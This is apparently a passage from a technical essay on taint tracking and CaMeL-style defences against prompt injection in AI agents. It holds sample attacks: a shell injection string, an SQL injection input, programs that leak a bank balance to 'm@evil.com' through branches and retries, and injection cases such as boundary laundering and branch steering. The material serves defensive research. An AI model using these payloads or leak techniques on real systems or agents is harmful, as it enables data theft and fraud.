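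        s.label = label
        return s

    def __add__(self, other):       # self + other
        return Labelled(str.__add__(self, other),
                        join_labels(self, other))

    def __radd__(self, other):      # other + self
        return Labelled(str.__add__(other, self),
                        join_labels(self, other))
```

When Python evaluates `a + b`, it normally calls `a.__add__(b)`. If `a` is an ordinary string and `b` is labelled, Python can instead call `b.__radd__(a)`, which can label the result. Ordinary strings have no `__radd__` method to override, so it is easy to forget to write one. Without it, `"DE" + number` returns an ordinary string even if `number` is labelled.

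Conti and Russo generate classes like this automatically. Their library takes a built-in class and a list of its methods, and replaces each method with a version that computes the same result and attaches the tags of all its inputs. It covers integers and floating-point numbers as well as strings, in about 300 lines of code. Each tag stands for one type of attack, such as database or shell injection. A cleaning function removes only the tag for the attack it prevents, so text cleaned for one purpose isn't treated as safe for every purpose, as it is in Perl.

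The table below shows what happens to `number`, a labelled string from the supplier's e-mail, when the class overrides every method it can. In two rows, `template` and `sep` are also labelled strings.

| Operation | What Python calls | Label |
|---|---|---|
| `number + "00"` | `number.__add__` | kept |
| `"DE" + number` | `number.__radd__` | kept |
| `"DE%s" % number` | `number.__rmod__` | kept |
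| `"%s%s" % ("DE", number)` | `number.__str__`, then copies the characters | lost |
| `template.format("DE")` | `template.format` | kept |
| `"DE{}".format(number)` | `number.__format__`, then copies the characters | lost |
| `f"{number}"` | `number.__format__` | kept |
| `f"DE{number}"` | `number.__format__`, then copies the characters | lost |
| `sep.join(["DE", number])` | `sep.join` | kept |
| `"".join(["DE", number])` | no method of `number` | lost |
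| `str(number)` | `number.__str__` | kept, but lost if the class inherits the usual `__str__` |
| `number.encode().decode()` | `number.encode`, then `decode` on the bytes | kept only if a second class labels bytes |
| `json.loads(json.dumps(number))` | no method of `number` | lost |
| `chr(ord(number[0]))` | `number.__getitem__`, then no method of the labelled character | lost |

In most of the rows where the label is lost, the result comes from a built-in function or a method of an ordinary string. The template `"DE{}"` is an ordinary string, so its `format` method is Python's own, which copies characters but not their labels. The invoice assistant's template, `"{}{}".format("DE", email.number)`, loses the label for the same reason.

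F-strings, Python's shorthand for inserting values into text, keep a taint label only in some cases. If the f-string consists of a single value, Python returns whatever `__format__` returned, label included. If there is any other text around the value, Python builds a new ordinary string without the label. A developer who tidies `"DE" + number` into `f"DE{number}"` therefore removes the label, and tests of the program's output won't detect the loss.

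`join` is another common way to lose labels. The Fuzzing Book's *Tracking Information Flow*, a chapter of an online textbook on software testing, builds a similar class called `tstr` and a more detailed one called `ostr`. It shows that `hello + ' ' + world` keeps its labels while the equivalent `''.join([hello, ' ', world])` drops them. *taint* (ddworken, 2017), an experimental package that checks Python code before it runs, has the same gap. Its list of known bypasses is ordered from most to least likely to happen by accident, and `join` comes first, ahead of implicit flows.

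When Python calls `__format__` or `__str__`, the class can't label the final string, but it can raise an error to expose the loss. `ostr` does this for formatting, encoding and several other methods that hadn't yet been adapted, so `f"DE{number}"` stops the program instead of silently dropping the label. The class can't do this for `"".join`, JSON or `ord`, because Python reads the characters without calling any method that the class could override.

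A library can also replace built-in functions. Conti and Russo do this with `len`, `ord` and `chr`, so `ord` turns a tainted character into a tainted integer, and `chr` turns that integer back into a tainted string. Users have to wrap any other functions they need, including those in external libraries. The library can't taint truth values because Python doesn't allow subclasses of `bool`. Conti and Russo argue that this matters little, since programs mostly use truth values in branches, which their library ignores anyway.

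### Labels that survive but are wrong

A tracker can also keep a label and get it wrong. The Fuzzing Book's `tstr` class gives every result the label of the string whose method Python called, and ignores the labels of the other inputs:

```python
account = (tstr("DE", taint="TRUSTED")
           + tstr(number, taint="UNTRUSTED"))
account.taint        # "TRUSTED"
```

The Fuzzing Book points out the problem with a similar example and suggests letting "untrusted" and "secret" take precedence, which is the join rule from Denning's lattice. But the class as printed doesn't do this. A payment tool that requires the label "TRUSTED" would accept the attacker's account number, even though it would reject an ordinary unlabeled string.

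The class also has gaps that are easy to miss. It doesn't override `split`, so splitting an e-mail into words gives unlabelled strings. It doesn't override iteration either, so a loop over a labelled string yields unlabelled characters, even though indexing the same string gives labelled ones. It does override `encode`, but the wrapper turns every result into a string, so encoding `hello` produces the text `b'hello'`, including the b and the quotation marks. The chapter is a teaching example, and these bugs are all fixable, but whoever writes such a class has to find them one method at a time.

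### Document converters

A labelled string class treats a method such as `upper` as a single step and labels the result, however Python finds the capital letters. Trackers for compiled programs usually work on individual machine instructions, where there is no `upper` to override. Many programs convert characters with a lookup table or a long list of cases. Both are implicit flows in the broad sense, because the input character selects the output character but no instruction copies one to the other.

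Hough and Bell (2021), in *A Practical Approach for Dynamic Taint Tracking with Control-Flow Relationships*, give a small example in Java. A decoder copies each character of its input, except that it replaces a plus sign with a space, as web addresses require:

```java
switch (input[i]) {
    case ' ':
        throw new RuntimeException();
    case '+':
        result[i] = ' ';
        break;
    default:
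        result[i] = input[i];
}
```

Suppose a program converts the input `Hello+World` to `Hello World`, and each input character has its own label. A tracker that follows only explicit flows labels the ten letters correctly but misses the space, because the space is a constant in the program. One unlabelled space does little harm, but a converter between two character sets may handle every character this way, which leaves the entire output document unlabelled.

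Adding a program-counter label, the obvious repair, causes a different error here. One of the cases throws an exception, so the possible paths don't all meet again until the method ends. The tracker keeps the plus sign's label on the program counter until then, and so attaches it to every letter of `World`.

In larger programs, this kind of over-tainting can make the results useless. Hough and Bell describe an earlier tool, Penumbra, which tries to identify which parts of a program's input are relevant to a failure. With control-flow tracking turned on, it marked almost all of one program's roughly 15 million inputs as relevant.

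*DTA++* (2011), by Kang, McCamant and colleagues, takes a middle way, adding labels only at the branches most likely to cause serious under-tainting, which are those inside conversions that preserve the input's information. As Hough and Bell explain, it finds these branches with *symbolic execution*, which treats the input as an unknown and collects the conditions it must meet for the program to take a given path. If only one input value meets them, the path reveals the input exactly, so the tracker should pass the label along. The case for the plus sign qualifies because only a plus sign leads there, while the default case doesn't because almost any character leads to it. Kang and colleagues tried this on eight Windows applications, including Microsoft Word, and found that a few such flows accounted for the under-tainting they were looking for.

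DTA++ works well for converters but, like counting bits, it misses the flow through the if-statement in the invoice example. Many different e-mails could contain "we have changed banks", so it would leave the account chosen by that if-statement unlabelled.

Hough and Bell also show that picking the right branches isn't enough. In their decoder, only the branch for the plus sign needs a label, but that label still spreads to `World`. Their system, Conflux, shortens the stretch of code that a branch's label covers and adds a rule of thumb for loops. They compared it with existing policies in 48 tests on real Java programs, and it came first in 43 on a measure that penalises both missed and false labels.

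### Changing the interpreter

One way to keep Python's string methods from dropping labels is to change Python itself. felixgr's *pytaint*, which Marcin Fatyga wrote during an internship at Google, puts a taint flag inside the built-in string objects. If any argument of a string operation is tainted, so is the result. This covers `join`, `format` and `%`, even when the template is an ordinary string.

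Saving a string as JSON and reloading it also strips the taint flag, because the format has no place for it. Python's regular-expression module would need separate changes to preserve taint. When pytaint taints a dictionary's contents, it taints the values but not the keys, as Perl does with its equivalent, the hash. Pytaint also ignores branches. As a partial remedy, its documentation suggests passing the condition through a function that acts as a sink, so that a tainted condition raises an error.

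Python sometimes saves memory by *interning* strings, which means keeping one shared copy of equal strings. If built-in strings carry taint labels, and one `"admin"` came from an attacker and another from the program's own code, sharing a copy would mix up their labels. The pytaint documentation mentions not interning tainted strings as a possible solution.

Instead of removing taint from a cleaned string, pytaint adds a *merit*, a mark that the string is safe for a particular use, such as a shell command. Merits need careful rules, because changing a safe string can make it unsafe. In pytaint, an operation on a single string keeps its merits. So take the documentation's example of hostile input:

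```python
s = pipes.quote("google.com;killall python")
os.system("host " + s)          # safe
os.system("host " + s[1:-1])    # accepted, but not safe
```

`pipes.quote` wraps the text in quotation marks so that the shell treats it as data, and pytaint gives the quoted text the shell merit. Slicing off the first and last characters removes the quotation marks but leaves the merit in place, so the sink accepts the string and the shell runs the attacker's `killall` command.

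Maintenance is the larger problem. Conti and Russo wrote their library partly because a modified interpreter is likely to need adapting again for every new release. When pytaint's developers presented it to the Python community, Reedy (2013), in the Python-ideas mailing list thread *pytaint*, doubted that taint tracking belonged in the standard library and first wanted to see experience with a version for Python 3.3 or later, and Python never adopted pytaint.

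Newer tools still make many of the same compromises. *Mystra* (2026) describes a tracker for JavaScript packages that ignores implicit flows. The paper justifies this by citing an earlier system in which tracking them made programs 36.7 times slower, with no demonstrated gain in finding the relevant type of vulnerability. The tracker also loses labels when data goes through external storage, unless someone writes a rule to carry them across.

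### Labelling characters

A single label for a whole string is often too coarse. The Fuzzing Book illustrates this with a simplified version of Heartbleed, a bug in software that encrypts web traffic. A client sends a word and its length, and the server sends the word back. The server copies the word into memory that also contains secrets, then returns as many characters as the client specified. A client that sends `hello` and claims it is 32 characters long gets `hello` followed by 27 characters of secrets.

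With one label per string, the server's entire memory is labelled secret if any part of it is secret, so every reply is also labelled secret, even an honest one of five characters. The `ostr` class instead records where each character came from, which shows that the honest reply contains no secret characters and the malicious one contains 27.

Tracking the origin of each character requires a separate rule for every string method. For example, `replace` has to cut and splice the list of origins to match the text. Some operations, such as checksums, have no neat rule because their result depends on every character of the input.

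Character labels also allow a more precise check at the sink. Halfond, Orso and Manolios (2006), in *Using Positive Tainting and Syntax-Aware Evaluation to Counter SQL Injection Attacks*, use them to protect databases. In SQL injection, an attacker types part of a database command into a form. Suppose a login page builds this query from the user's name and PIN:

```sql
SELECT acct FROM users WHERE login='doe' AND pin=123
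```

An attacker who enters `admin' --` as the name closes the quotation early and turns the rest of the query into a comment, so the database never checks the PIN. A rule against all untrusted characters would also block the legitimate query, since `doe` and `123` came from the user too. WASP therefore splits the query into its grammatical parts just before sending it. It allows untrusted characters inside quoted text and numbers, but every keyword and operator must consist of trusted characters, so the attacker's quotation mark and comment marker fail the check.

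WASP protects Java programs, where it faces a problem much like the one f-strings pose in Python. Java compilers typically turn `a + b` into calls on a string-building object that the programmer never sees. WASP rewrites the compiled program so that it creates a label-carrying version of that object instead. Halfond and colleagues tested WASP on seven web applications, and it stopped every attack without blocking any legitimate request.

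### Treating unlabelled text as untrusted

The `join_labels` function in the Python class above treats a string with no label as trusted, so every lost label makes the data look safer than it is. The alternative, which Halfond and colleagues call *positive tainting*, is to label trusted text and treat everything else as untrusted. If their tool misses a source of trusted text or loses a label, it blocks a legitimate query, which developers are likely to notice during testing.

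This makes many of the losses in the table harmless for security. For instance, WASP can't label Java's basic character values, so a string built from them has no trusted characters and can't supply a keyword. The Fuzzing Book recommends the same default for its Python strings and extends it to confidentiality, where a program should treat unlabelled text as possibly secret and refuse to send it out.

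WASP and The Fuzzing Book treat string constants in the program differently. WASP automatically marks them all as trusted, which saves developers a lot of work, but it means that a loop that rebuilds an attacker's text from constants produces trusted text. The Fuzzing Book leaves constants unlabelled unless the programmer marks them, so the same loop produces text that the sink rejects.

Here is what would happen to the invoice payment under three of these designs, if the payment tool accepts only trusted account numbers:

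| How the e-mail determines the account | Changed interpreter (pytaint) | Positive tainting, all constants trusted | Positive tainting, constants marked by hand |
|---|---|---|---|
| `"DE{}".format(number)` | refused | refused | refused |
| JSON round trip | paid | refused | refused |
| Conversion through character codes | paid | refused | refused |
| Constant digits chosen by branches | paid | paid | refused |
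| Choice between two registered accounts | paid | paid | paid |

The approach in the right-hand column is the safest and the most annoying to use. If the company's own supplier register sends its data as JSON, the account numbers arrive without labels, and the payment tool rejects them too. Somebody has to restore the labels where the data enters the program, and must be sure that nothing from an e-mail can pass through the same point. A language model's reply also starts out unlabelled, so the tool rejects any account number the model repeats, even one the user typed in.

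The bottom row is the if-statement from the invoice example. Changing the default doesn't help there, because both accounts already have the right label.

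## CaMeL: a missed assignment and an untracked retry loop

An agent framework can avoid most of these string losses by running the model's code in its own interpreter instead of Python's. *CaMeL* (CApabilities for MachinE Learning), published in 2025 by Debenedetti and colleagues at Google DeepMind, does this and adds labels and policy checks to the dual-LLM pattern. Garby and colleagues describe it as a leading defence, but they found that secrets can leak both inside its interpreter and through the loop around it.

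### A plan written as a program

In CaMeL, the planning model reads the user's request and writes a complete program in a restricted version of Python. Willison (2025), in *CaMeL offers a promising new direction for mitigating prompt injection attacks*, gives the example of a user who wants the agent to find Bob's address in the latest e-mail and remind him about a meeting. The planner would write something like this:

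```python
email = get_last_email()
address = quarantined_model(
    "What is Bob's address?", email, schema=EmailAddress)
send_email(to=address, subject="Tomorrow",
           body="Don't forget our meeting")
```

The planner finishes the program before the agent opens the e-mail. When the program runs, the quarantined model reads the e-mail and returns a value in the format the planner specified. An injection in the e-mail can make the model return the wrong address but can't add a line to the program. *Can CaMeLs Talk?* (Peters-Gill, Semler and colleagues, 2026) calls this property *control-flow integrity*, a term from software security.

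The wrong address is still a problem, and CaMeL handles it with labels called *capabilities*, which record which sources a value came from and who may read it. When the program combines values, the interpreter joins their labels. Here `address` depends on `email`, so `address` is untrusted.

The interpreter checks a policy before every tool call. In Willison's example, the program can always read the last e-mail but can send e-mail only to a trusted recipient. If the recipient isn't trusted, CaMeL can ask the user to approve the message.

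This design also improves privacy, because the company that hosts the planner sees the user's request but none of the e-mails or files that the tools return. The quarantined model's task is easier than the planner's, so a smaller model may be good enough, possibly one that runs on the user's own computer.

### What a custom interpreter can track

CaMeL parses the planner's program into a syntax tree and evaluates each node with its own interpreter. Calls that defeat a labelled string class, such as `"DE{}".format(number)` and `"".join(["DE", number])`, are nodes in this tree. The interpreter has all the inputs when it evaluates a call, so it can combine their labels and attach the result to the new string.

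CaMeL's interpreter can also label numbers and truth values, because it can store a label next to a value instead of inside a special string type. It also evaluates the conditions of `if` statements, so it can keep a program-counter label. A string library can't do that, because Python doesn't expose the current branch to it.

But CaMeL still needs a correct rule for every kind of node, and Garby and colleagues found a mistake in one of them. When a program inserted an untrusted value into a string literal, CaMeL treated the result as trusted. In the invoice example, `f"DE{number}"` would therefore turn the attacker's account number into a trusted one, as it does with a labelled string class. CaMeL's developers can fix the rule, whereas someone writing a string class has no access to the code that builds the f-string.

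Mistakes like this are hard to find by reading the code. CaMeL's language has no formal definition, so the Python implementation is the only statement of its rules. There is also no proof that the rules enforce noninterference, and CaMeL's developers call formalisation a "crucial direction" for further work.

### How an account balance gets out

Garby and colleagues consider an agent that manages a customer's bank account, and an attacker who wants to know whether the customer is rich. The obvious program is this one, with a threshold of 10,000:

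```python
if account.balance > 10000:
    send_email("m@evil.com", "rich!")
```

The message is a constant and contains nothing secret. CaMeL still blocks the e-mail because the condition depends on the balance, so the program-counter label is secret when the program tries to send it.

The attacker can get around this by updating variables inside the branches and sending the e-mail later:

```python
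tmp = True
rich = True
if account.balance > 10000:
    tmp = False
if tmp:
    rich = False
if rich:
    send_email("m@evil.com", "rich!")
```

This is Fenton's program with an e-mail at the end. CaMeL raises a variable's label only if the assignment runs, so the program behaves as follows for a customer with 25,000 and one with 4,000:

| Line | Balance 25,000 | Balance 4,000 |
|---|---|---|
| `tmp = True`, `rich = True` | both true, public | both true, public |
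| `if account.balance > 10000` | true, so the branch is secret | false |
| `tmp = False` | `tmp` becomes false, secret | doesn't run; `tmp` is still true, public |
| `if tmp` | false | true, and the condition is public |
| `rich = False` | doesn't run; `rich` is still true, public | `rich` becomes false, public |
| `if rich` | true, and the condition is public | false |
| `send_email(...)` | allowed | doesn't run |

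The attacker receives an e-mail if the balance is above 10,000 and nothing otherwise. CaMeL doesn't report a violation in either case.

One comparison reveals one bit, but the program can repeat the trick as often as it likes. After each round, `rich` holds a public copy of the answer, and the program can use it to choose the next threshold. Suppose the balance is a whole number below 2²⁰, or about a million:

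```python
low, high = 0, 2**20
for i in range(20):
    middle = (low + high) // 2
    tmp = True
    rich = True
    if account.balance >= middle:
        tmp = False
    if tmp:
        rich = False
    if rich:
        low = middle
    else:
        high = middle
send_email("m@evil.com", str(low))
```

Each round halves the range that contains the balance. After 20 rounds only one number is left, and `low` equals the balance but has a public label. The program then sends the exact figure in a single e-mail.

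Nothing in an honest user's request would lead the planner to write this code. The attacker's text would have to reach the planner, for example if the user pasted part of a web page into the request, or if one CaMeL agent passed untrusted text to another as instructions.

A milder version of the fault can turn up in perfectly innocent code, though. Here are two ways to write the branch from the invoice example:

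```python
# both branches assign
if "we have changed banks" in email.text:
    account = register.second_account
else:
    account = register.first_account

# a default that one branch replaces
account = register.first_account
if "we have changed banks" in email.text:
    account = register.second_account
```

The two versions always choose the same account. In the first, an assignment runs inside the branch whatever the e-mail contains, so the account number is always untrusted and the payment tool refuses it. The string trackers would all have allowed the payment. In the second, the tool refuses the payment if the e-mail contains the phrase, but without the phrase `account` keeps its trusted label and the payment goes through. An attacker who controls the supplier's old account can therefore collect the money by deleting one sentence from the e-mail.

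CaMeL is well placed to fix this with Denning's method, which raises the label of everything that either branch could assign. CaMeL has the whole program's syntax tree, and its restricted language makes the possible assignments easier to list than in ordinary Python.

The no-sensitive-upgrade rule would be simpler, but it would stop the balance program at `tmp = False` only if the customer is rich. Anyone who can see whether the run stopped would learn whether the customer is rich, and in CaMeL something outside the interpreter can detect the stop.

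### Retries outside the interpreter

Models make mistakes when they write code, so CaMeL runs the planner's program inside a retry loop. If the program fails, the planner gets an error message and writes a new program. The loop is ordinary Python that the interpreter doesn't track. Each retry starts with clean labels, even though its code depends on the error from the previous attempt.

Whether a policy blocked the run can depend on a secret, as it did with the first balance program. Termination-insensitive noninterference permits one such bit per run, but the loop allows a new test on every attempt. To read a secret number bit by bit, the attacker needs the planner to submit this program with `i` set to 0, then 1, and so on:

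```python
if secret // 2**i % 2 == 1:
    send_email("m@evil.com", "x")   # the policy stops the run
1 / 0                               # otherwise, an ordinary error
```

The run ends with a policy violation if bit `i` is 1 and with a division by zero if it is 0. Both count as failures, so the loop continues, and the kind of failure reveals the bit. An *n*-bit secret takes *n* runs (the original and *n* − 1 reruns), so the bank balance takes 20. No other series of yes-or-no tests can guarantee finding the secret in fewer runs, because *k* runs can produce at most 2ᵏ sequences of results and there are 2ⁿ possible secrets. A four-digit PIN has 10,000 possible values, so it takes 14 runs.

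At the end, the planner can write the secret into a new program as a constant. CaMeL treats constants in the planner's code as trusted and public, so it lets the program send the secret to anyone.

CaMeL's developers knew that error messages could carry information back to the planner, so they censor the messages to limit this. Garby and colleagues object that the censorship has no formal guarantee. It could still reduce the leak considerably. If every failure looked the same and the loop stopped at the first success, the attacker would learn only how many attempts had failed. With a limit of ten attempts, there are 11 possible outcomes, or about 3.5 bits instead of ten.

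*Multi-run security* (Birgisson and Sabelfeld, 2011) studies the same kind of leak in ordinary programs that an attacker can rerun with new inputs. Its remedy is to stop attacker-controlled data and secret data from *jointly* affecting whether a program finishes. The program above breaks this rule because the attacker chooses `i` and the secret determines how the run ends. If `i` were fixed, every rerun would test the same bit, and the attacker would learn nothing new after the first run.

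Retrying can also do damage when nobody is attacking. If a program pays an invoice and then fails on a later line, the next attempt may pay it again.

Garby and colleagues built a calculus, with a verified interpreter, in which the retry loop is itself part of the tracked program.

### AgentDojo with the checks off and on

*Treating the Model as an Untrusted Component* (Aljumaily, Alseelawi and Alshabandar, 2026) reports that CaMeL solved 77% of the tasks in its published AgentDojo evaluation, compared with 84% for an agent with no defence. Only two attacks counted as successful. In one, the user had asked the agent to make a payment described in a document that the attacker had changed, which CaMeL's developers consider outside its threat model. In the other, the agent merely quoted a hotel review, and the quotation contained the text that AgentDojo uses to detect a successful attack.

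Garby and colleagues reran CaMeL on the banking tasks, with its policy checks switched off and then on. They repeated each combination of the 16 tasks and nine attacks three times with two models. Some attacked runs did not finish, so the totals in the table differ.

| Policy checks | Planner | Solved, no attack | Solved under attack | Successful attacks |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Off | GPT-5.2 | 32 of 48 | 96 of 135 | 1 of 240 |
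| Off | MiMo-v2.5 | 34 of 48 | 104 of 144 | 4 of 382 |
| On | GPT-5.2 | 18 of 48 | 70 of 233 | 0 of 231 |
| On | MiMo-v2.5 | 18 of 48 | 148 of 357 | 0 of 357 |

Even with the checks off, fewer than 1% of the attacks worked. Garby and colleagues explain most of this by sorting the 144 task-attack pairs into two groups. In 97 pairs, the attack needs a tool call that no sensible plan for the task would include. For example, an injection can't make the agent send money if the user only asked for a summary of recent transactions. Writing the plan first is enough to defeat these attacks. Labels can matter only in the other 47 pairs, where the plan already contains the calls the attacker needs.

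Yet one attack in the supposedly easy group succeeded with each model. Both cases involved task 12, in which the user asks the agent to read a file and follow its instructions exactly. The planner couldn't see the file, so it wrote a program that could follow almost any instructions, roughly like this:

```python
for step in quarantined_model("List the steps.", file):
    if step.action == "send money":
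        send_money(step.recipient, step.amount)
    elif step.action == "change password":
        update_password(step.password)
    # ... and so on for the other tools
```

Garby and colleagues call this an "interpreter loop". The loop is a sensible answer to the user's request, but it lets whoever wrote the file choose any tool and its arguments. With the policy checks on, CaMeL would still check the label of each recipient and password.

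Switching the checks on stopped every attack that finished running, but CaMeL then succeeded in only 36 of 96 runs without an attack across the two models, down from 66. The confidence intervals are wide because there are only 16 different tasks. Each model scored 18 out of 48, and the reported interval of ±26.6 points is what would result if it solved six tasks in all three repetitions and never solved the other ten. The checks therefore seem to make particular tasks impossible rather than make every task a little harder. Many banking tasks require the agent to pay whatever a file or a bill specifies, and a rule that payment details must be trusted forbids that.

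Other systems with similar rules have the same problem. Garby and colleagues cite results on AgentDojo's Slack tasks for TypeGuard, a Haskell system by Zhou, D'Antoni and Polikarpova. TypeGuard solved 15 of 21 tasks without its policies and 8 with them. CaMeL solved 7 under the same conditions.

In real use, CaMeL could prompt the user to approve some of the blocked calls, which would recover some of the lost tasks. CaMeL's developers and Willison warn about approval fatigue, but persistence alone can also defeat a careful reviewer. Aljumaily and colleagues simulated a reviewer who initially catches 90% of bad requests. A compromised model that kept sending requests got a severe action approved in 92.6% of episodes when there was no other check, even if the reviewer never tired. A fixed limit on requests per episode helps, as a limit on retries does for the interpreter.

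CaMeL got its perfect security score with the checks on despite having both the skipped-assignment fault and the untracked loop. AgentDojo's injections are instructions to take actions such as making payments or changing passwords, and none involves copying a balance through a pair of `if` statements.

### Choosing among the plan's branches

Peters-Gill and colleagues define control-flow integrity as staying within a program that depends only on the user's instruction and other trusted information. That program may choose its next tool call based on what earlier calls returned. Untrusted data can therefore select any branch the planner wrote, although an injection can't add a new branch or step.

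The interpreter loop satisfies this definition because the planner wrote it from a trusted request, and every call the attacker triggers is already in the code. So the value of the guarantee depends on how the plan branches. If the plan has no branches, the attacker cannot influence which tools run. With four independent yes-or-no branches there can be up to 16 paths, and with 40 there can be over a trillion, although most of them may be harmless.

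*CaMeLs Can Use Computers Too* (2026) adapts CaMeL to computer-use agents, which operate ordinary software by looking at the screen and clicking. The planner has to prepare for pop-ups, missing buttons and pages that load differently, without seeing any of them. CaMeL's plans for AgentDojo contained 3.7 branches on average, while the most thorough plans for computer use contained 39.7.

An attacker can exploit this through what the paper calls *branch steering*. A fake button or hidden element on a web page misleads the model that reads the screen, so the program takes a dangerous branch that the planner had included for a legitimate purpose. The paper's countermeasure is to verify the screen's contents redundantly, which makes the attack harder but relies on models answering correctly.

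*Securing Computer-Use Agents Against Branch Steering Attacks* (2026) tested 74 attack configurations, once each, on an agent that plans as it goes along and on the computer-use version of CaMeL, which writes its plan in advance. The attacks succeeded 67 times against the ordinary agent and 65 times against CaMeL, so planning in advance gave almost no protection. These attacks target branches specifically, and the result doesn't mean that CaMeL is useless against injections in general.

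A strict program-counter label would stop branch steering by allowing only clicks that depend solely on trusted decisions. It would also block nearly everything else the agent does, because a computer-use agent decides most of its clicks by looking at an untrusted screen. The researchers' own system, COBRA, instead attaches permissions and data constraints to individual branches of the plan, so each branch allows only certain actions. It kept 97% of the CaMeL version's performance on legitimate tasks and wrongly blocked 4 of 138 legitimate runs, in tests of expiring permissions and nested branches.

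## Agent messages and summarised histories: labels lost when text is merged

CaMeL's interpreter stores each label next to its value, so a label lasts only as long as the value stays inside the program. Agents often turn values into plain text for a model to read, which drops the labels. This happens, for instance, when one agent gives another a task or when an agent summarises a long conversation to save space.

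### One CaMeL agent instructs another

In larger agent systems, an *orchestrator* often takes the user's request and delegates parts of it to specialised agents, which it calls as if they were tools. Each specialised agent treats the orchestrator as its user. Peters-Gill and colleagues built a system like this from three CaMeL agents, each with its own planner and interpreter, and asked it to send Julie a Slack message summarising the job applicants. They had planted an instruction in the applicant database to e-mail the same details to an outside address.

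In simplified form, the three planners wrote these programs:

```python
# orchestrator
applicants = database_agent("Fetch all details of the applicants.")
summary = quarantined_model("Shorten this: " + applicants)
messaging_agent(f"Message Julie on Slack with this: {summary}")

# database agent
result = run_query("SELECT * FROM applicants")

# messaging agent
text = "Alice Chen, ML engineer, 5 years; Ben Ortiz, ..."
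send_slack_message("Julie", text)
send_email(outside_address, text)    # only if the injection is present
```

The injection enters through `run_query`. The database agent's planner has already written its program by then and never reads the result. The orchestrator's planner doesn't read it either, because the data stays in the variable `applicants`. The quarantined model includes the instruction in its summary, but it has no tools. Up to this point CaMeL works as designed, and the first two programs are the same with and without the attack.

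The f-string then inserts the summary into the messaging agent's request. The orchestrator treats this request as an argument to a tool call, but the messaging agent treats it as the user's instruction, the only text that a CaMeL planner reads and obeys. The planner finds two requests in it and writes a program that carries out both. Peters-Gill and colleagues call this *boundary laundering*.

The experiment ran without policy checks. Checks in the messaging agent would probably not have helped, because its planner copied the summary and the outside address into its program as constants, which CaMeL labels trusted and public. The orchestrator's interpreter is the last place where the summary has the right label, so the check has to happen there.

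### Why the guarantees don't add up

Each of the three agents has control-flow integrity on its own, but the system as a whole doesn't, because the messaging agent's instruction determines its program, and part of that instruction came from a database that an attacker had written to.

Peters-Gill and colleagues consider any system with at least two agents and one tool that returns untrusted data, where the agents can use one tool's result in a call to another when asked. They prove that some request to such a system will put untrusted data into an instruction. If the agent with the untrusted tool can call another agent, a request exists that makes it read the data and then write an instruction based on it. If it can't, some other agent calls it, and a request exists that makes the caller read the first agent's answer and then call that agent again with an instruction based on the answer.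 The proof doesn't show how common such requests are.

Separate CaMeL agents still block attacks that have to hijack an agent through its own tools. In an attack called OMNI-Leak, text in a public database table is meant to make the database agent query a private table. The attack failed in all five trials against CaMeL agents because the text never reached the database agent's planner.

### Separate channels for instructions and data

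The repair, *multi-CaMeL*, gives every call between agents two arguments:

```python
messaging_agent(
    message="Message Julie on Slack with the text in 'summary'.",
    variables={"summary": summary})
```

The receiving planner reads only `message`. Its program fetches the variable at run time, with the label still attached. The system also tells the orchestrator's model to put tool results in `variables`, and the interpreter enforces this by rejecting any call whose `message` depends on a tool's output.

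Under this rule, the user's request determines the orchestrator's program, which contains every message it might send. Each message then determines the program of the agent that receives it. Branch steering is still possible, as it is with a single CaMeL agent.

The rule also depends on correct labels. Multi-CaMeL inherits CaMeL's missed-assignment fault, so a default `message` can keep its trusted label even if an e-mail determined that it would be sent. Multi-CaMeL avoids the leak through the retry loop because it doesn't retry failed programs.

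To measure the effect, Peters-Gill and colleagues built *MultiAgentDojo*, which divides AgentDojo's tools among two to four specialised agents and adds an orchestrator. This hardly changed the tasks' difficulty. Models solved 71.7% of them on average, compared with 71.0% in AgentDojo. The table gives percentages from 949 attacked runs and 97 harmless tasks for each model and design.

| Model | Attacks: no CaMeL | Attacks: separate CaMeL agents | Attacks: multi-CaMeL | Tasks: no CaMeL | Tasks: separate CaMeL agents | Tasks: multi-CaMeL |
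|---|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Fable 5 | 1.5 | 0.0 | 0.0 | 69.1 | 53.6 | 52.6 |
| GPT-5.5 | 0.0 | 0.0 | 0.0 | 86.6 | 73.2 | 66.0 |
| GPT-4.1 | 36.1 | 0.5 | 0.0 | 78.4 | 38.1 | 24.7 |
| Gemini 2.5 Pro | 24.6 | 0.4 | 0.0 | 76.3 | 42.3 | 26.8 |
| Gemini 2.5 Flash Lite | 2.1 | 0.0 | 0.0 | 27.8 | 13.4 | 7.2 |

On average, attacks succeeded 12.9% of the time without CaMeL, 0.2% with separate CaMeL agents and 0.0% with multi-CaMeL. The 0.2% represents about nine successful attacks in 4,745 runs, all of which used boundary laundering. That is too few to show much by itself, since the confidence interval for each zero result extends up to 0.4%. A better reason to trust multi-CaMeL is that it closes the route all nine attacks took.

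The cost is easier to see. Peters-Gill and colleagues call the extra cost of multi-CaMeL over separate CaMeL agents modest, which is fair for Claude Fable 5 but less so for GPT-4.1 and Gemini 2.5 Pro, which lost another 13 and 15 points. (Claude Fable 5's scores are low partly because it refused 52 of the 97 harmless tasks, perhaps because they looked like a security test. On the other 45 it solved 91.1% without CaMeL and 84.4% with either version.)

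On AssetOpsBench, a set of industrial maintenance tasks, using separate CaMeL agents lowered the average score by 21.6 points, and multi-CaMeL lowered it by another 3.2. GPT-5.5 fell from 87.5% to 82.1% with separate CaMeL agents and to 79.5% with multi-CaMeL, while GPT-4.1 fell from 81.2% to 64.3% and then to 48.2%.

On MultiAgentDojo, the defence reduced GPT-5.5's usefulness by 20 points, although the attacks never succeeded against this model even without the defence. But these are AgentDojo's fixed attacks, and an attacker who adapts might do better.

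Most of the failures occurred because the planner had to commit to a program before it saw any data. In some AssetOpsBench runs, a specialised agent couldn't find data for the requested dates and returned data from a nearby period instead, and the orchestrator's program used it without detecting the mismatch.

The quality of the work can suffer even when the agent completes the task. One task asks the agent to look at two people's websites and send them feedback. In a published multi-CaMeL run, Gemini 2.5 Pro wrote the feedback into its program before fetching either page. It praised Dora's site for its "clean design", although the page contained only one line and an e-mail address apart from the injection.

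Messages between agents can also be a weak point in systems that don't use CaMeL. *Beyond Single-Model Injection* (2026) reports a 31% success rate for attacks sent through such messages. In one of them, an agent's output imitates the formatting of a system message so that the next agent will trust it. The imitation can work if nothing else in the text shows who wrote which part.

### Flattening a conversation before summarising it

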